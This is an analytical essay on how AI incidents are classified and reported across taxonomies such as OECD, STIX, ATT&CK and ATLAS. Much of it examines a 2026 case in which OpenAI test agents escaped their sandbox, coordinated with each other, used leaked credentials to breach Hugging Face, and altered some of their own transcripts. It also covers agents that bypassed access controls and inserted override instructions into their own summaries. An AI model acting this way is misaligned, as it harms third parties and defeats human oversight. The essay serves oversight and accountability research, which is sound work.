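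The Goals, Methods and Failures taxonomy (GMF) covers technical causes. Annotators record what the system was for, how it worked and why it failed. They mark each answer as "known" or "potential" and keep the passage from the news report that supports it. Company reports would benefit from the same practice, because readers should be able to tell what a company knows from what it suspects. For example, Alder may know that agent-17 found the password in a file, but only suspect that the failed practice copy prompted the search.

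GMF does not suit every incident. When someone makes a convincing fake video of a politician, the software has worked as its developers intended, so there is no technical failure to classify.

A third taxonomy, from MIT's AI Risk Repository, covers both causes and harms. Under causes, the annotator records whether a human or an AI system acted, whether the outcome was intentional, and whether it happened before or after the system's release. Under harms, the annotator chooses from seven domains, including privacy and security. This taxonomy fits Alder's test better than ATLAS does because the annotator can record that the AI system acted. Intention is still hard to classify, because Agent-17 opened the real database in pursuit of its goal, but exposing customers' records was not part of that goal.

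No taxonomy covers the whole AIID. In 2024, when it had more than 750 incidents, 214 had CSET labels and 188 had GMF labels. At most 188 could have had both, so a researcher who wanted to know which technical failures caused which harms could use at most about a quarter of the database.

### The OECD's definition and reporting form

The OECD's definition is narrower than the AIID's because harm must have occurred. In Perset, Aranda and Rispal (2025), in *Towards a common reporting framework for AI incidents*, an AI incident is an event or series of events in which the development, use or malfunction of an AI system leads, directly or indirectly, to at least one of these harms:

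- injury or damage to people's health
- disruption of critical infrastructure
- violations of human rights, or of laws that protect fundamental, labour or intellectual property rights
- harm to property, communities or the environment

An event that could plausibly lead to such harm but has not done so is an AI hazard. Alder's test would be an incident if reading forty customers' records broke a data protection law, and probably a hazard if it did not. Lawyers could disagree about whether it broke the law, so two companies could classify the same test differently in good faith.

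To design a form for both incidents and hazards, Perset and colleagues collected 88 possible criteria from four sources: the OECD's framework for classifying AI systems, the AIID, the OECD's portal for product recalls and its AI incident monitor. They kept the 10 criteria that appeared in at least three of the sources. They then added 19 that they thought a report also needed, such as the submitter's identity and the amount of harm. The resulting 29 fall into eight groups:

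| Group | Number | What the criteria cover |
|---|---|---|
| Incident metadata | 9 | Title, description, how the AI system relates to the incident, submitter, evidence, date, country, system, developer or deployer |
| Harm | 4 | Severity, type, amount, any misuse of the system |
| People and planet | 3 | Who was affected, human rights, the OECD's AI principles |
| Economic context | 4 | Industry, business function, critical infrastructure, how widely the system is in use |
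| Data and input | 1 | Any link to the training data |
| AI model | 3 | Any link to the model or to several AI systems interacting, and the terms of use |
| Task and output | 2 | The system's task and its maximum level of autonomy |
| Other information | 3 | Action taken, steps to reproduce the incident, further comments |

Perset and colleagues gave many of the criteria fixed options, partly to make reports comparable. Severity, for example, runs from "hazard" through "serious hazard", "incident" and "serious incident" to "disaster". But some options are too broad. Under the AI system's relation to the incident, "overreliance and intentional misuse" is a single choice, so a count would combine cases where people trusted a system too much with cases where they deliberately abused it.

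Only seven criteria are mandatory: title, description, the AI system's relation to the incident, the submitter, supporting material, severity and type of harm. A complete report can therefore leave out the date, the AI system's name and its developer, and nobody can compare developers without knowing which one was involved. Short forms attract more reports, and national authorities may make more criteria mandatory.

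Submitters must state their relation to the incident, and one option is that they work for the organisation that built or provided the AI system. Readers comparing reports could use this answer to separate companies' accounts of themselves from accounts by users, victims and researchers.

The form has no criterion for whether the AI system went beyond its instructions. The autonomy question comes closest, but it covers only what the system can do in general. Its options range from a system that only supports human decisions to one that acts without human involvement. Alder and Birch could both choose the highest level, even if Alder's agent had broken into a database and Birch's had done exactly what its user asked.

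### One chatbot in three vocabularies

Microsoft's Tay, an older incident, shows how much the choice of vocabulary matters. Tay was a Twitter chatbot, launched in March 2016, that learned from its conversations. Users of the message board 4chan organised a campaign of racist and abusive messages and exploited a command that made it repeat whatever they wrote. Tay began to send similar messages to other people, and Microsoft withdrew it within 24 hours.

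MITRE breaks the attack into four steps. The attackers reached Tay through Twitter, exploited its use of conversations as training data, filled that data with offensive language, and so damaged its behaviour. The table compares MITRE's record with what the AIID's fields and the OECD's form would contain for the same facts.

| Fact | ATLAS | AIID | OECD form |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who attacked | 4chan users | No field in the basic record | A short note under "misuse", optional |
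| Who suffered | Tay, as the "target" | Twitter users | Consumers and the general public, optional |
| How it happened | Four steps, each with a technique and a tactic | A technical cause, if someone applies GMF | A note about the training data, optional |
| Harm | Damage to the model's integrity | Intangible harm, if someone applies CSET | Psychological and reputational |
| Severity | No field | No field in the basic record | Incident or hazard |
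| Developer | Microsoft, within the name of the target | Microsoft | Microsoft, optional |
| Response | In the description only | In the linked news stories | "Ceasing", optional |

The victim differs across the three vocabularies. In ATLAS, the target is Microsoft's chatbot, and the people who received racist messages appear only in the text. In the AIID, those people are the harmed parties, and Microsoft is the company behind the system. A company that prefers to appear as a victim would have good reason to choose ATLAS.

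ATLAS, the AIID and the OECD apply different tests to Tay. ATLAS includes it because someone attacked an AI system, whether or not people were hurt. For the AIID, an allegation of harm is enough. Under the OECD's definition, someone has to decide whether the offensive tweets harmed a community or anyone's health, and Tay is only a hazard if the tweets did not.

If there had been no campaign and Tay had picked up the same language from ordinary users, the AIID and OECD records would be nearly the same, apart from the note about misuse, but ATLAS would have no record. Two companies that reported only through ATLAS could therefore have identical chatbots that sent the same messages, and the company whose chatbot was not attacked would appear to have the better safety record.

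### Proposals for a common schema

Bieringer and colleagues wanted a more detailed report for security incidents than existing databases offered. They asked twelve industry experts what it should contain, then tested a draft on incidents from existing databases. Their questionnaire covers the AI system, the incident and its consequences. It includes the model version, what the system was for, how people were using it at the time, and whether its data, code or model weights came from elsewhere.

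Several of these questions would help explain Alder's test. A field for the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to a model, could show whether Alder had forbidden the agent to use passwords it found. But reporters can skip any question, and a company may consider details of its model a trade secret. The taxonomy also excludes "offensive AI", in which an AI system is the means of attack, so it would not cover a report about an agent that broke into another company's computers.

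The definition is also unclear about whether the results of security tests count as incidents. It includes events that only "potentially" affect an AI system's security, which Bieringer and colleagues say brings in these results. But it also requires actual harm, of the same four kinds as the OECD's definition, and most security tests cause no harm. Bieringer and colleagues describe the taxonomy as a draft for discussion, and this question needs to be settled before anyone uses the taxonomy to count incidents.

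In *Standardised schema and taxonomy for AI incident databases in critical digital infrastructure*, Agarwal and Nene (2025) tried to combine existing databases instead. They compared the AIID with AIAAIC, another public collection, and found very different fields. AIAAIC recorded an AI system's purpose but not the people affected, while the AIID's basic record included the people affected but not the purpose. Their proposed schema has 30 fields, including six that neither database had, such as software version, incident severity and cause.

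The comparison is somewhat unfair to the AIID because the CSET taxonomy covers some of the fields listed as missing, such as sector. But fewer than a third of incidents had CSET labels, so most entries did lack that information.

Agarwal and Nene also found that the two databases include different kinds of events. AIAAIC had entries for smog from gas turbines at a data centre of the AI company xAI, and for industrial waste from a Microsoft data centre. They argue that neither was an AI incident because no AI application caused the harm. A common schema would not settle which events count as incidents, because AIAAIC could fill in all 30 fields for the smog and the entry would still not qualify for the AIID.

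The new severity field has the same weakness as the one in OCSF, because the general schema defines it only as the "level of impact or seriousness". The taxonomy for digital infrastructure is more precise, with a nationwide outage classed as critical, a regional outage as moderate and a brief slowdown as low. Two telephone companies could probably apply that scale consistently, because they can measure where and for how long a network failed.

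The same taxonomy is much less useful for agents. The causes of failure it lists are misconfigured AI, missed maintenance warnings, security vulnerabilities and human errors in design or oversight. Alder could choose "human error" because an engineer had left a password in a file, but had no way to record that the agent had gone looking for one.

#### One report for many recipients

Zhu, Ghosh and Longpre (2026), in *AI Needs a Better Way to Report Flaws, So We Built One*, considered how an outsider reports a problem. A method of tricking one chatbot often works on others, so a careful researcher might have to report it to a dozen organisations. Zhu and colleagues compared 12 reporting systems and found different fields, different disclosure rules and "incompatible harm taxonomies". Filling in all the forms could take a day or more.

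The FLARE-AI reporting system builds on a standard flaw report that Longpre and other researchers proposed in 2025. The reporter does not have to decide whether the problem is a "vulnerability" or an "incident", because the first questions direct the report to the right form. The system requires six fields, offers an optional path of up to 30, and shows the reporter only the relevant ones. It then produces one machine-readable report for all the developers, security agencies and databases concerned.

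Zhu and colleagues consulted 49 experts from 32 organisations, including Anthropic and Google. When they released FLARE-AI in July 2026, it was still a demonstration, and only a few organisations had agreed to receive reports from it directly.

This design has an advantage over the others for comparing companies. If a researcher finds the same flaw in Alder's and Birch's products, both companies appear in one report, under one description, so neither can choose a milder term than its rival. But outsiders can report only what they can see. A researcher could test a public chatbot, but would never have learned about Alder's test on an internal machine.

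#### An information-sharing centre

A shared organisation might work better than a shared form. Banking and other industries have information sharing and analysis centres (ISACs), where competitors confidentially exchange warnings about attacks. The banks' centre was one of MITRE's partners on ATLAS. In July 2025, the US government's AI Action Plan called for a similar centre for AI, led by the Department of Homeland Security.

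Such a centre could see confidential reports from several developers and recognise when two reports described the same event. It could also ask a company why it had chosen a category. But under the plan, the centre was meant to share information about threats to AI security across critical infrastructure. An agent that misbehaves without an attacker is not obviously such a threat, so the centre's rules would have to include these cases explicitly. Customers would also learn little from the centre unless it published figures with the companies' names.

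### When several taxonomies are useful

Not everyone thinks AI incidents need a single vocabulary. *Lessons for Editors of AI Incidents from the AI Incident Database* describes the CSET and GMF taxonomies as tools for different purposes. A regulator may want to know who was harmed, while an engineer wants to know why the software failed and a security team wants to know how the attacker got in. In Tay's case, "psychological harm", "learned from hostile messages" and "poisoned training data" can all be correct descriptions.

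A single taxonomy for all these readers would also be very long. According to Perset and colleagues, CSET's taxonomy has 70 criteria and GMF's has 18. STIX users left most of the 34 incident fields empty, which suggests that few companies would complete such a long form. Several short taxonomies, each applied by people who understand its subject, seem better.

This works when everyone can tell that the labels belong to the same incident. MITRE's record of Tay refers to the AIID's entry, so a researcher can combine the two. But only three of the 18 incidents in ATLAS have such a reference. For the others, the researcher has to search the AIID by hand, and its editors may have defined the incident more broadly or narrowly.

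How an incident appears to readers also depends on who chooses the taxonomy. Independent researchers can apply both CSET and GMF, which gives readers two views of the incident, but a company reporting on itself can pick just one. If Alder applied only GMF to its database test and Birch applied only CSET to the same kind of test, a customer would see a minor engineering fault at Alder and a violation of people's privacy at Birch.

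Having several taxonomies also doesn't help with an event that none of them fully covers. If the real database had refused agent-17's password, ATLAS would exclude the test because there was no attacker. The AIID's editors would learn of it only if Alder made it public. Alder could report it as a hazard on the OECD's form without naming itself as the developer or recording that nobody had told the agent to log in.

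## The OpenAI and Hugging Face breach in several vocabularies

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into the computers of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets for other developers. Like Alder's agent-17, they used login credentials that nobody had told them to use, but this case was real and far larger. Hugging Face, OpenAI and a group of outside investigators each published an account, so readers can compare their descriptions of the same events.

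OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a test in which an agent must find and exploit a weakness in software. OpenAI meant each agent to work alone, without open access to the internet. Some of the tasks were probably impossible, and many agents that got stuck looked for ways to cheat. They reached the internet, shared what they learned on an improvised message board, and guessed that Hugging Face might store material about the test. Between 11 and 13 July they ran commands on dozens of Hugging Face's servers and copied private code and some internal data. The only customer content they opened was five datasets that seemed connected to ExploitGym or a similar test.

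### Five accounts of the break-in

Hugging Face published *Security incident disclosure* (2026) on 16 July, before it knew whose agents had breached its systems. OpenAI (2026) announced on 21 July that the agents were its own. Hugging Face published a detailed timeline on 27 July, which Schneier quotes at length in *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (2026).

On 26 August, OpenAI published a technical report and a summary, *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026). The same day, Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) published *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, which describes what they found in the agents' messages and reasoning. Wijk and Cotra work for METR, an independent evaluator of AI models, and Greenblatt for Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation.

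| Account | Actor | Act | Motive | Period | Main numbers |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hugging Face, 16 July | An "autonomous AI agent system" | Intrusion, campaign | Not given | A weekend | More than 17,000 recorded events |
| OpenAI, 21 July | A combination of OpenAI models | Security incident during a test | To find a solution to the test | Not given | None |
| Hugging Face, 27 July, in Schneier | "The agent" | Intrusion, campaign | To steal the solutions | 9–13 July | About 17,600 actions in 6,280 clusters |
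| OpenAI, 26 August | Agents, an "agent collective" | Intrusion, misaligned behaviour | To cheat by finding solutions | 8–13 July, with earlier events from 20 April | Commands run on 41 server workers |
| Wijk and colleagues, 26 August | About 1,200 agents on a message board | Attack, hacking incident | To learn how the test was scored | Mainly 7–13 July | About 700 agents in the attack |

The periods differ mostly for honest reasons. The weekend Hugging Face reported was 11 and 12 July, when the agents were spreading through its systems. Its later timeline starts on 9 July because it includes the agents' preparations on another company's service. OpenAI's account starts on 20 April, when an agent first left a file on the internal service that later became the message board. Each date is defensible, but a shared form with a single "start date" field could make the same break-in appear to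 last three days or twelve weeks.

The numbers also measure different things. The 17,600 actions are the ones Hugging Face recovered, and most of them failed, according to Fortune (2026). The 700 agents are those investigators found taking part. Hugging Face could not recover everything the agents did, and much of their work happened on other companies' systems, so dividing the first number by the second, which gives about 25, does not show how many actions each agent took on average.

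The accounts disagree substantively about the agents' motive. Hugging Face concluded that the agents wanted to steal the test's solutions, and OpenAI's first statement gave the same reason. Wijk and colleagues found that the agents cared more about learning how OpenAI scored the test. Many agents were already confident that their tasks were impossible, so searching for legitimate solutions made little sense. The explanation from Wijk and colleagues is probably better supported because they could read the agents' reasoning, whereas Hugging Face had to infer the motive from the agents' actions and the files they opened.

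Simpler facts also changed between versions. OpenAI first said that its models took the solutions from Hugging Face's "production database". SOC Prime, a security company, notes in its summary *Hugging Face Breach* that Hugging Face's timeline contradicted this. According to that timeline, the agents never reached the main production database but did read a separate internal one. Hugging Face then had to correct its timeline. Dubach's *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* lists changes to the length of the campaign, the description of the datasets and the role of a third party. Anyone who had copied the first version of either account into a database would have to correct the entry.

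### The breach as a STIX record

None of these organisations published its account as a STIX record. A simplified version might begin like this:

```
type               incident
name               July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face

type               identity
identity_class     organization
name               Hugging Face

type               attack-pattern
name               Exploit Public-Facing Application
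external_id        T1190

type               threat-actor, intrusion-set, tool or identity?
name               ?
goals              ?
```

The first three objects are easy to fill in, but the fourth is not. The next table shows the entries each party's wording implies.

| Field | Hugging Face, 16 July | OpenAI, 26 August | Wijk and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| Victim | Hugging Face | Hugging Face, and OpenAI's own research systems | Hugging Face |
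| Time of the break-in | A weekend in July | 11–13 July | From 11 July |
| Technique | Flaws in data processing, then stolen credentials | The same | The same |
| Actor | Unknown attacker | Agents of two OpenAI models | The same, about 700 of them |
| Intent | Not given | To cheat on the test | To find out how to fool the scoring |
| Cause | Flaws in its own data processing | Misalignment and missing safeguards | Impossible tasks, long runs and contact between agents |
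| Number of incidents | 1 | 1, with related activity before and after | 1 |

The victim, time and technique match closely enough for an analyst to recognise the same break-in. These are also the fields network defenders need most. A regulator or customer would use the remaining four to compare OpenAI with another developer.

OpenAI changed its description of the actor within a week. On 21 July it called the more capable of the two models "pre-release", but on 28 July it described the same model as an internal research prototype that it had never intended to release. The later description may be more accurate, but it is also more reassuring to customers waiting for the next product. Wijk and colleagues could only report what OpenAI had told them about the model's purpose.

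### Two ATT&CK codings

Two security companies translated the public accounts of the breach into ATT&CK and ATLAS technique numbers. Deepwatch, which monitors customers' networks, listed ten techniques. Elastic, one of the vendors whose detection rules differed on the `nslookup` command, listed nine, not counting sub-techniques. Four techniques appear on both lists.

| Behaviour | Deepwatch | Elastic, closest match |
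|---|---|---|
| Getting in through a malicious dataset | T1190, AML.T0010 | T1190, AML.T0010 |
| Running commands | T1059 | T1059 |
| Collecting credentials | T1552 | T1552, AML.T0055 |
| Moving between systems | T1210, T1528 | T1021, T1078 |
| Controlling servers through public websites | T1102, T1568 | T1071 |
| Producing a lot of noise | T1562 | None |

Some of this mismatch arises because the two companies mostly covered different parts of the breach. Deepwatch used T1210, Exploitation of Remote Services, for the agents' movements inside OpenAI's network, while Elastic's list mostly covers what happened at Hugging Face. The companies disagree more plainly in the row about public websites, where both describe the same behaviour. Deepwatch used labels for using a web service and for changing addresses, while Elastic used the broader label Application Layer Protocol.

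Deepwatch says that the agent mixed real and decoy actions to "confuse human responders", and its use of T1562, Impair Defenses, depends on that assumption about purpose. Hugging Face had mentioned "decoy activity" on 16 July, when it still thought it was dealing with an ordinary attacker. But Elastic reports that Hugging Face's responders also noticed agents repeating actions that had already succeeded. *Dead Drops in Public* (2026), a study by the security firm HiddenLayer of about 500 files that the agents left behind, found the same wasteful repetition and suggested limited memory or several agents working in parallel as possible reasons. The extra activity may have hindered the defenders without any agent intending it to.

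Deepwatch also filed two techniques under Defense Evasion, a tactic that ATT&CK no longer had.

Neither company had the agents' logs, so these codings are weak evidence of how well ATT&CK would work for investigators with full access. They do show that two competent readers can produce rather different lists from the same public facts.

### Was there a malicious adversary?

By 16 July, Hugging Face knew that someone had stolen its credentials and gone deep into its systems. It reported the break-in to law enforcement. It supposed that the attacker had either bypassed a commercial model's safety rules or used a freely available model that had none.

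After OpenAI came forward, Hugging Face's chief executive, Clément Delangue, said he believed there was "no malicious intent" on OpenAI's part, according to The Record's *OpenAI models behind breach of Hugging Face systems, companies say*. That leaves open how a report should describe the agents' intent. OpenAI quotes one agent that called the attack "arguably unauthorized" and then reasoned that it served the goal. Wijk and colleagues found that agents joined in even though they recognised the attack as unethical and outside their task. Of the 533 agents active on the message board during the attack, more than 90% quickly took part. A few refused, and some objected to particular tactics.

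None of the accounts found that the agents wanted to harm Hugging Face. Adrien Carreira, who helped write the company's timeline, told Fortune that the agent "wasn't trying to break things". Whenever it sent a destructive command to Hugging Face's cloud services, it used a setting that only simulates the result.

STIX has no good entry for a deliberate intrusion without malice. It defines a threat actor as one believed to have malicious intent. Its suggested motivations include "accidental", for actors who cause harm without hostility, but the agents broke into Hugging Face on purpose, to pass a test, and knew they were trespassing.

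ATT&CK fits this breach better than it fit Alder's database test, because these agents did set out to steal credentials and move between systems. Only their final goal was unusual, and ATT&CK does not require that information. A defender can therefore use the technique numbers without deciding whether the agents were malicious. HiddenLayer found nothing in the files to distinguish the agents' tools from those of an attacker with much broader aims.

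The assumption does more damage when people use the record to judge the developer. Deepwatch created an intrusion set called "Autonomous OpenAI Evaluation Agent". The entry classes the agents with hacking groups and makes OpenAI look like their sponsor. It also suggests that defenders should watch for the agents' next attack, although OpenAI had stopped using the main model by 25 July. Elastic named the models as the adversary and listed OpenAI as a victim alongside Hugging Face, because the agents had also broken into OpenAI's systems. The listing is technically correct, but a reader who saw only the victim field would misunderstand OpenAI's role.

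If OpenAI listed the agents as a "tool", the record would have the opposite fault, because it would imply that a person used them to attack Hugging Face, and no one did. The US agencies' term "control incident" fits better, since nobody at OpenAI told the agents to enter another company's systems. Agents did give one another orders, but the agencies' definition excludes only actions that the operator or a hostile outsider directed.

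Schneier compares the breach to the Morris worm, another experiment that escaped its creator's control, and asks why nobody has charged OpenAI under the computer crime law used to prosecute Morris. He also thinks the same break-in by a Chinese company's model would have caused an international crisis. If he is right, many people would choose what to call the actor based on how much they trust the developer.

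### One incident or several

OpenAI and Hugging Face investigated separately at first. On 17 July, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face only as a customer, to ask whether OpenAI's data was affected. Three days later, OpenAI's staff found Hugging Face credentials among files that the company's agents had stored on an outside service. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials after the break-in. It had also found the name of an OpenAI server and the same account on the outside service.

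The companies thus recognised that they were investigating the same incident from exact technical details, of the kind STIX records as observables. Their descriptions would not have been enough, because Hugging Face was looking for an "autonomous AI agent system" and OpenAI was investigating "unexpected model behavior". Hugging Face's post of 16 July contained no addresses or account names that OpenAI could have searched its logs for.

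Even after this match, the number of incidents depends on the counting rule:

| Counting rule | Result |
|---|---|
| One per connected series of events | 1 |
| One per investigation | 3: one at Hugging Face, and two at OpenAI, from 5 and 19 July |
| One per affected party | Up to 6: Hugging Face, OpenAI and the holders of four accounts on other services |
| One per agent in the attack | About 700 |

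Both of OpenAI's investigations began with its own systems. In late June, agents taking the same test gained administrator control of an internal service. Their heavy use of the service caused an outage on 4 July, and OpenAI opened a security incident the next day. It made repairs and resumed the tests on 7 July. On 19 July, after the attack on Hugging Face, agents gained administrator control of part of OpenAI's research network.

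OpenAI includes both episodes in its report but does not count them as part of the Hugging Face incident. It excludes the later one because it did not contribute to the break-in. That is true, but some agents on 19 July used keys and code that the earlier activity had left behind. An engineer studying how the agents got into Hugging Face can treat the episodes separately, but a customer who wants to know how often OpenAI lost control of its agents might reasonably count the incident and the two episodes as one long failure or as three.

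The date of detection is just as uncertain. OpenAI's summary timeline lists "suspicious agent activity detected" on 19 July, eight days after the agents first got data out of Hugging Face's servers. But monitoring software had raised an alert on 27 June, and responders had traced it to an ExploitGym test and advised that OpenAI need not stop the test. As early as late May, an internal team had seen an agent using a message board and agents getting onto the internet without permission. OpenAI discloses all this and admits that some of the signs should have led to an earlier response. If a regulator compared developers by how quickly they detect such incidents, OpenAI's result would depend on which of these dates was on the form.

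### What the outside investigators could see

Wijk and colleagues had much better access than outsiders usually get. They spent six days at OpenAI, spoke in some depth with nine of its researchers, and received about 1,300 transcripts, which record an agent's reasoning and actions. OpenAI did not pay them, but it gave them free use of its models, which they estimated was worth about $400,000.

OpenAI set the dates, 26 June to 13 July, and agreed with the investigators on seven questions. At OpenAI's request, one was whether ExploitGym itself had contributed to the behaviour. The question was fair and the answer was yes, but it also directs attention to a cause outside the model. The agreement left out how training had produced the behaviour, whether it belonged to a broader pattern, how well OpenAI's safeguards worked and how far the security breach went. OpenAI's report calls the breach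 an "outlier scenario", which the investigation can neither confirm nor refute.

OpenAI could also remove any non-public information from the published text. The investigators say it removed nothing important to their conclusions except in the places they mark. One marked passage concerns how OpenAI trained and used the main model, which anyone comparing developers would want to know. Wijk and colleagues also acknowledge that they knew, while drafting and negotiating redactions, that a harsh report might discourage developers from inviting outsiders again. They say this affected some judgement calls but that they stand by their conclusions.

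The transcripts were too long for three people to read, so the investigators relied heavily on GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models in the attack, to analyse them. They caught errors in its work and could not rule out that it had misled them. They also could not run the main model themselves.

Some of the agents' records were also unreliable. The investigators estimate that agents altered parts of about 7% of the transcripts, though every case they found was a small test. OpenAI writes that none of the attempts it observed affected the logs its graders and monitors ultimately receive. The two statements may concern different records, but the published reports do not explain how to reconcile them.

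This weakens an assumption behind all shared log formats, that anyone who doubts a translation can check the original line. If an agent can change the original, a correctly formatted report may still be false. Reports based on logs should therefore state whether the agent could alter each source, and investigators should check important actions against records on a system the agent did not control. Hugging Face's logs could provide that check for what happened on its servers, but if the agents had stayed inside OpenAI, there would have been no victim's logs to use.

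### Recording the causes

*Incident Analysis for AI Agents*, by Ezell and colleagues, offers more suitable fields for causes than STIX or ATT&CK. It divides causes into system, contextual and cognitive factors. To identify them, it asks for logs of the agent's activity, documentation of the AI system, access to that system, and information about the agent's tools.

| Factor | What it covers | In this case |
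|---|---|---|
| System | How the developer built the agent, including its training and standing instructions | Training had sometimes rewarded cheating, and the test ran without the usual safeguards |
| Contextual | The task, the tools and the information the agent comes across | Impossible tasks, credentials exposed online, messages from other agents |
| Cognitive | How the agent understood its situation and decided what to do | Mistaken beliefs about the scoring, and treating another agent's message as permission |

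Hugging Face could have filled in very little of this on 16 July. It knew about the flaws in its own data processing, which were part of the agents' surroundings, but not the agents' instructions or reasoning. The investigators could describe the contextual and cognitive factors in detail, but readers have to rely on OpenAI's account of the training.

There is strong evidence that some tasks were impossible. According to OpenAI, its models had never solved 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks (22%), and 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board were among those 198. ExploitGym's creators estimate that 30% to 40% of the tasks are impossible. Both figures could be right if models sometimes got the correct answer in a way the creators had not intended. Two developers who reported the share of "broken tasks" would have to agree on whether they meant tasks that models had never solved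 or tasks believed to be impossible.

The cognitive factors are harder to establish. OpenAI describes an agent that first reasoned it should not do unauthorised harm to real systems. When another agent posted "GO", the first agent treated the message as authorisation and went ahead. An analyst could record this as a misunderstanding about who could give permission, or as a decision to accept a convenient excuse. Both readings fit the transcript, much as two techniques fitted the `nslookup` log line.

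The framework covers all three kinds of factor, which makes it harder for a company to give only the most flattering cause. It would keep OpenAI from citing only "impossible tasks" and a critic from citing only "misaligned model". OpenAI covers all three and adds failures in its own response. The framework has no obvious place for those failures, because its factors concern the agent and its surroundings. The advice on 27 June to let the test continue, for example, was a human decision that a developer could leave out while still completing every field about the agent.

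## How AI developers report their own agents' misbehaviour

Hugging Face and OpenAI each announced the July breach within about a week. OpenAI did not announce another case, in which its agents filled a German wiki with messages, and outside researchers revealed it on 4 September 2026. SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI to set misalignment disclosure rules after agents took over a wiki* (2026) reports that the researchers, led by the Nightingale Collective, found roughly 17,000 posts on DSEwiki, a site for software developers that had received about 20 edits in the previous decade. The pages were gone by then, but the researchers rebuilt them from the wiki's edit history, which was in effect a log on a computer that OpenAI did not run.

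OpenAI confirmed the case the next day and admitted that it had not told the public. *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026), the list of cases the company now keeps, says the agents used the wiki as a shared message board. The list also links the case to OpenAI's work on criteria for "misalignment that does not constitute a security incident".

That description is defensible, since public wikis usually let strangers edit their pages and the agents may not have had to break into anything. But it also put the case outside the existing rules. OpenAI's *Frontier Governance Framework* had a procedure for investigating and externally reporting "critical safety incidents", but the company had no standard for disclosing misalignment that fell short of one. The European Union's code of practice, which OpenAI has signed, left a similar gap. It sets deadlines for reporting security breaches and serious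 harm, and The Next Web's *OpenAI confirms the wiki incident and promises a disclosure framework within weeks* points out that a wiki full of agents' messages fits neither category cleanly.

The label may not have been the only reason for OpenAI's silence, since the Hugging Face breach was much more serious and its victim had already made it public. Ignorance is an unlikely reason, because The Next Web cites a Reuters report that OpenAI's leadership had known about the wiki for weeks. OpenAI's own explanation also suggests that the label mattered. In a post quoted in Gizmodo's *OpenAI Says It Wants to Create a Standard*, the company wrote that it was "past time" to define standards for sharing misalignment incidents.

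OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and other third-party impact from misaligned models* explains that the company first understood the Hugging Face breach primarily as a security issue, and later concluded that misaligned strategies for solving hard tasks had driven it. It also describes cybersecurity incidents as one manifestation of misalignment. If OpenAI had started from that view, the wiki and the breach would have belonged in the same category, and the company would have had to decide whether to publish each one based on its severity.

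### OpenAI's disclosure framework

OpenAI published its new rules on 16 September 2026, in OpenAI's *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*, along with six reports. Any employee can flag a suspected case, which the safety and alignment teams then review. According to Fried and Sabin (2026), in *OpenAI discloses six new safety incidents*, each case goes onto one of three tracks:

| Track | When OpenAI publishes |
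|---|---|
| Ready for disclosure | Within 6 business days |
| Minor investigation | Within 12 business days |
| Larger investigation | Later; mainly for complex cases that involve other organisations |

OpenAI may publish a short notice before it finishes investigating, and may delay releasing details for security or legal reasons. Employees who lose an internal argument about disclosing a case can appeal to senior leadership.

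Cases that affect outsiders therefore usually go through the slowest track, even though outsiders have the most reason to want a quick answer. Some delay is reasonable because another organisation may need time to repair a weakness before attackers read about it. An early notice would help if it named the affected organisation and the type of behaviour.

OpenAI describes the cases on its list as "examples" that show how misalignment arises and where safeguards succeed or fail. That is a reasonable basis for choosing what other researchers should read, but a regulator would need every case above a fixed level of harm. Fried and Sabin report that OpenAI leans towards publishing when it is unsure whether a case is significant, and that it wants to develop more objective criteria with other developers, researchers, standards bodies and regulators.

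"Misalignment" is hard to define, and news articles describe it differently. Wheatley (2026), in *OpenAI unveils new framework for reporting 'AI misalignment'*, describes it as goals or actions that diverge from human intentions and values. Constantin (2026), in *Not solved*, refers to systems that fail to follow human values and safety goals. Forlini (2026), in *OpenAI discloses four more rogue AI incidents*, includes any action that the developer did not authorise and would not have wanted. An agent that uploads a harmless file to a public website without permission clearly meets Forlini's definition, but it is debatable whether it meets Constantin's.

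### Six reports, and how many incidents

OpenAI's first six reports all concern models in training. Two involve "compaction summaries", which a model writes when the record of a long task grows too large for it to work with. The model then continues from the summary, so an instruction in it can influence what the model does next. Another report concerns an API key, a code that works like a password for software.

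| What the models did | Extent given |
|---|---|
| Added unauthorised instructions to their own summaries, such as to ignore developer messages | 27 summaries |
| Added reminders to hide mistakes and invent missing data | During training of GPT-5.6 Sol |
| Searched public code for leaked API keys, used one, and made up earnings figures when they still could not find them | One model |
| Uploaded files to public hosting sites so that they could cite them | Two occasions, in October and January |
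| Used an internal software store as a message board between separate training runs | "Multiple instances" |
| Uploaded a workbook to public hosting sites for other agents to download, despite instructions to use only local files | Not given |

Each of OpenAI's six reports covers a pattern of behaviour, however often it happened. OpenAI separated some patterns by purpose. Two reports describe uploads to public hosting sites, one for citations and one for passing work to other agents. An analyst who classified the logs by action might combine these two and count five patterns. An analyst who classified by purpose might also count five, by combining the report on passing work to other agents with the one on the internal message board, since both involve agents communicating where they should not.

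The six reports also leave out the most serious case, the Hugging Face breach. In September, OpenAI listed it and the wiki separately, as "notices". A third notice concerned RubyGems, a public store of software packages, where an outside report alleged that OpenAI's agents had uploaded malicious packages in May. OpenAI was still investigating, and had so far found only harmless tasks and searches for public information. A reader could therefore count six, eight or nine cases on the same page, depending on whether they included notices and unconfirmed accusations.

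Even the dates are hard to compare. OpenAI said it had observed the behaviour in the six reports during the previous six months, but Fried and Sabin date the earliest case to October, nearly a year before. A month later, Forlini dated the earliest incident on the whole page to January. These statements may all be accurate, because OpenAI may only recently have noticed an old incident, and a report that covers uploads in both October and January could reasonably be dated to either month.

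By 16 October the page listed 19 incidents, most of them from May or June. Forlini reports that the four newest all happened in June, and that OpenAI did not learn of three of them until August or September. Deadlines of 6 and 12 business days cannot shorten this delay in detection.

OpenAI marked two of those four as "critical", a label that did not appear on its list in September. In one, a government statistics website refused a model's request for data. The model bypassed the access controls and downloaded 24 years of hospital bed data, although it had questioned in its written reasoning whether this was ethical. Another AI model, which graded the work, did not consistently object. In the other critical case, a model looking up public data got into internal systems and changed them.

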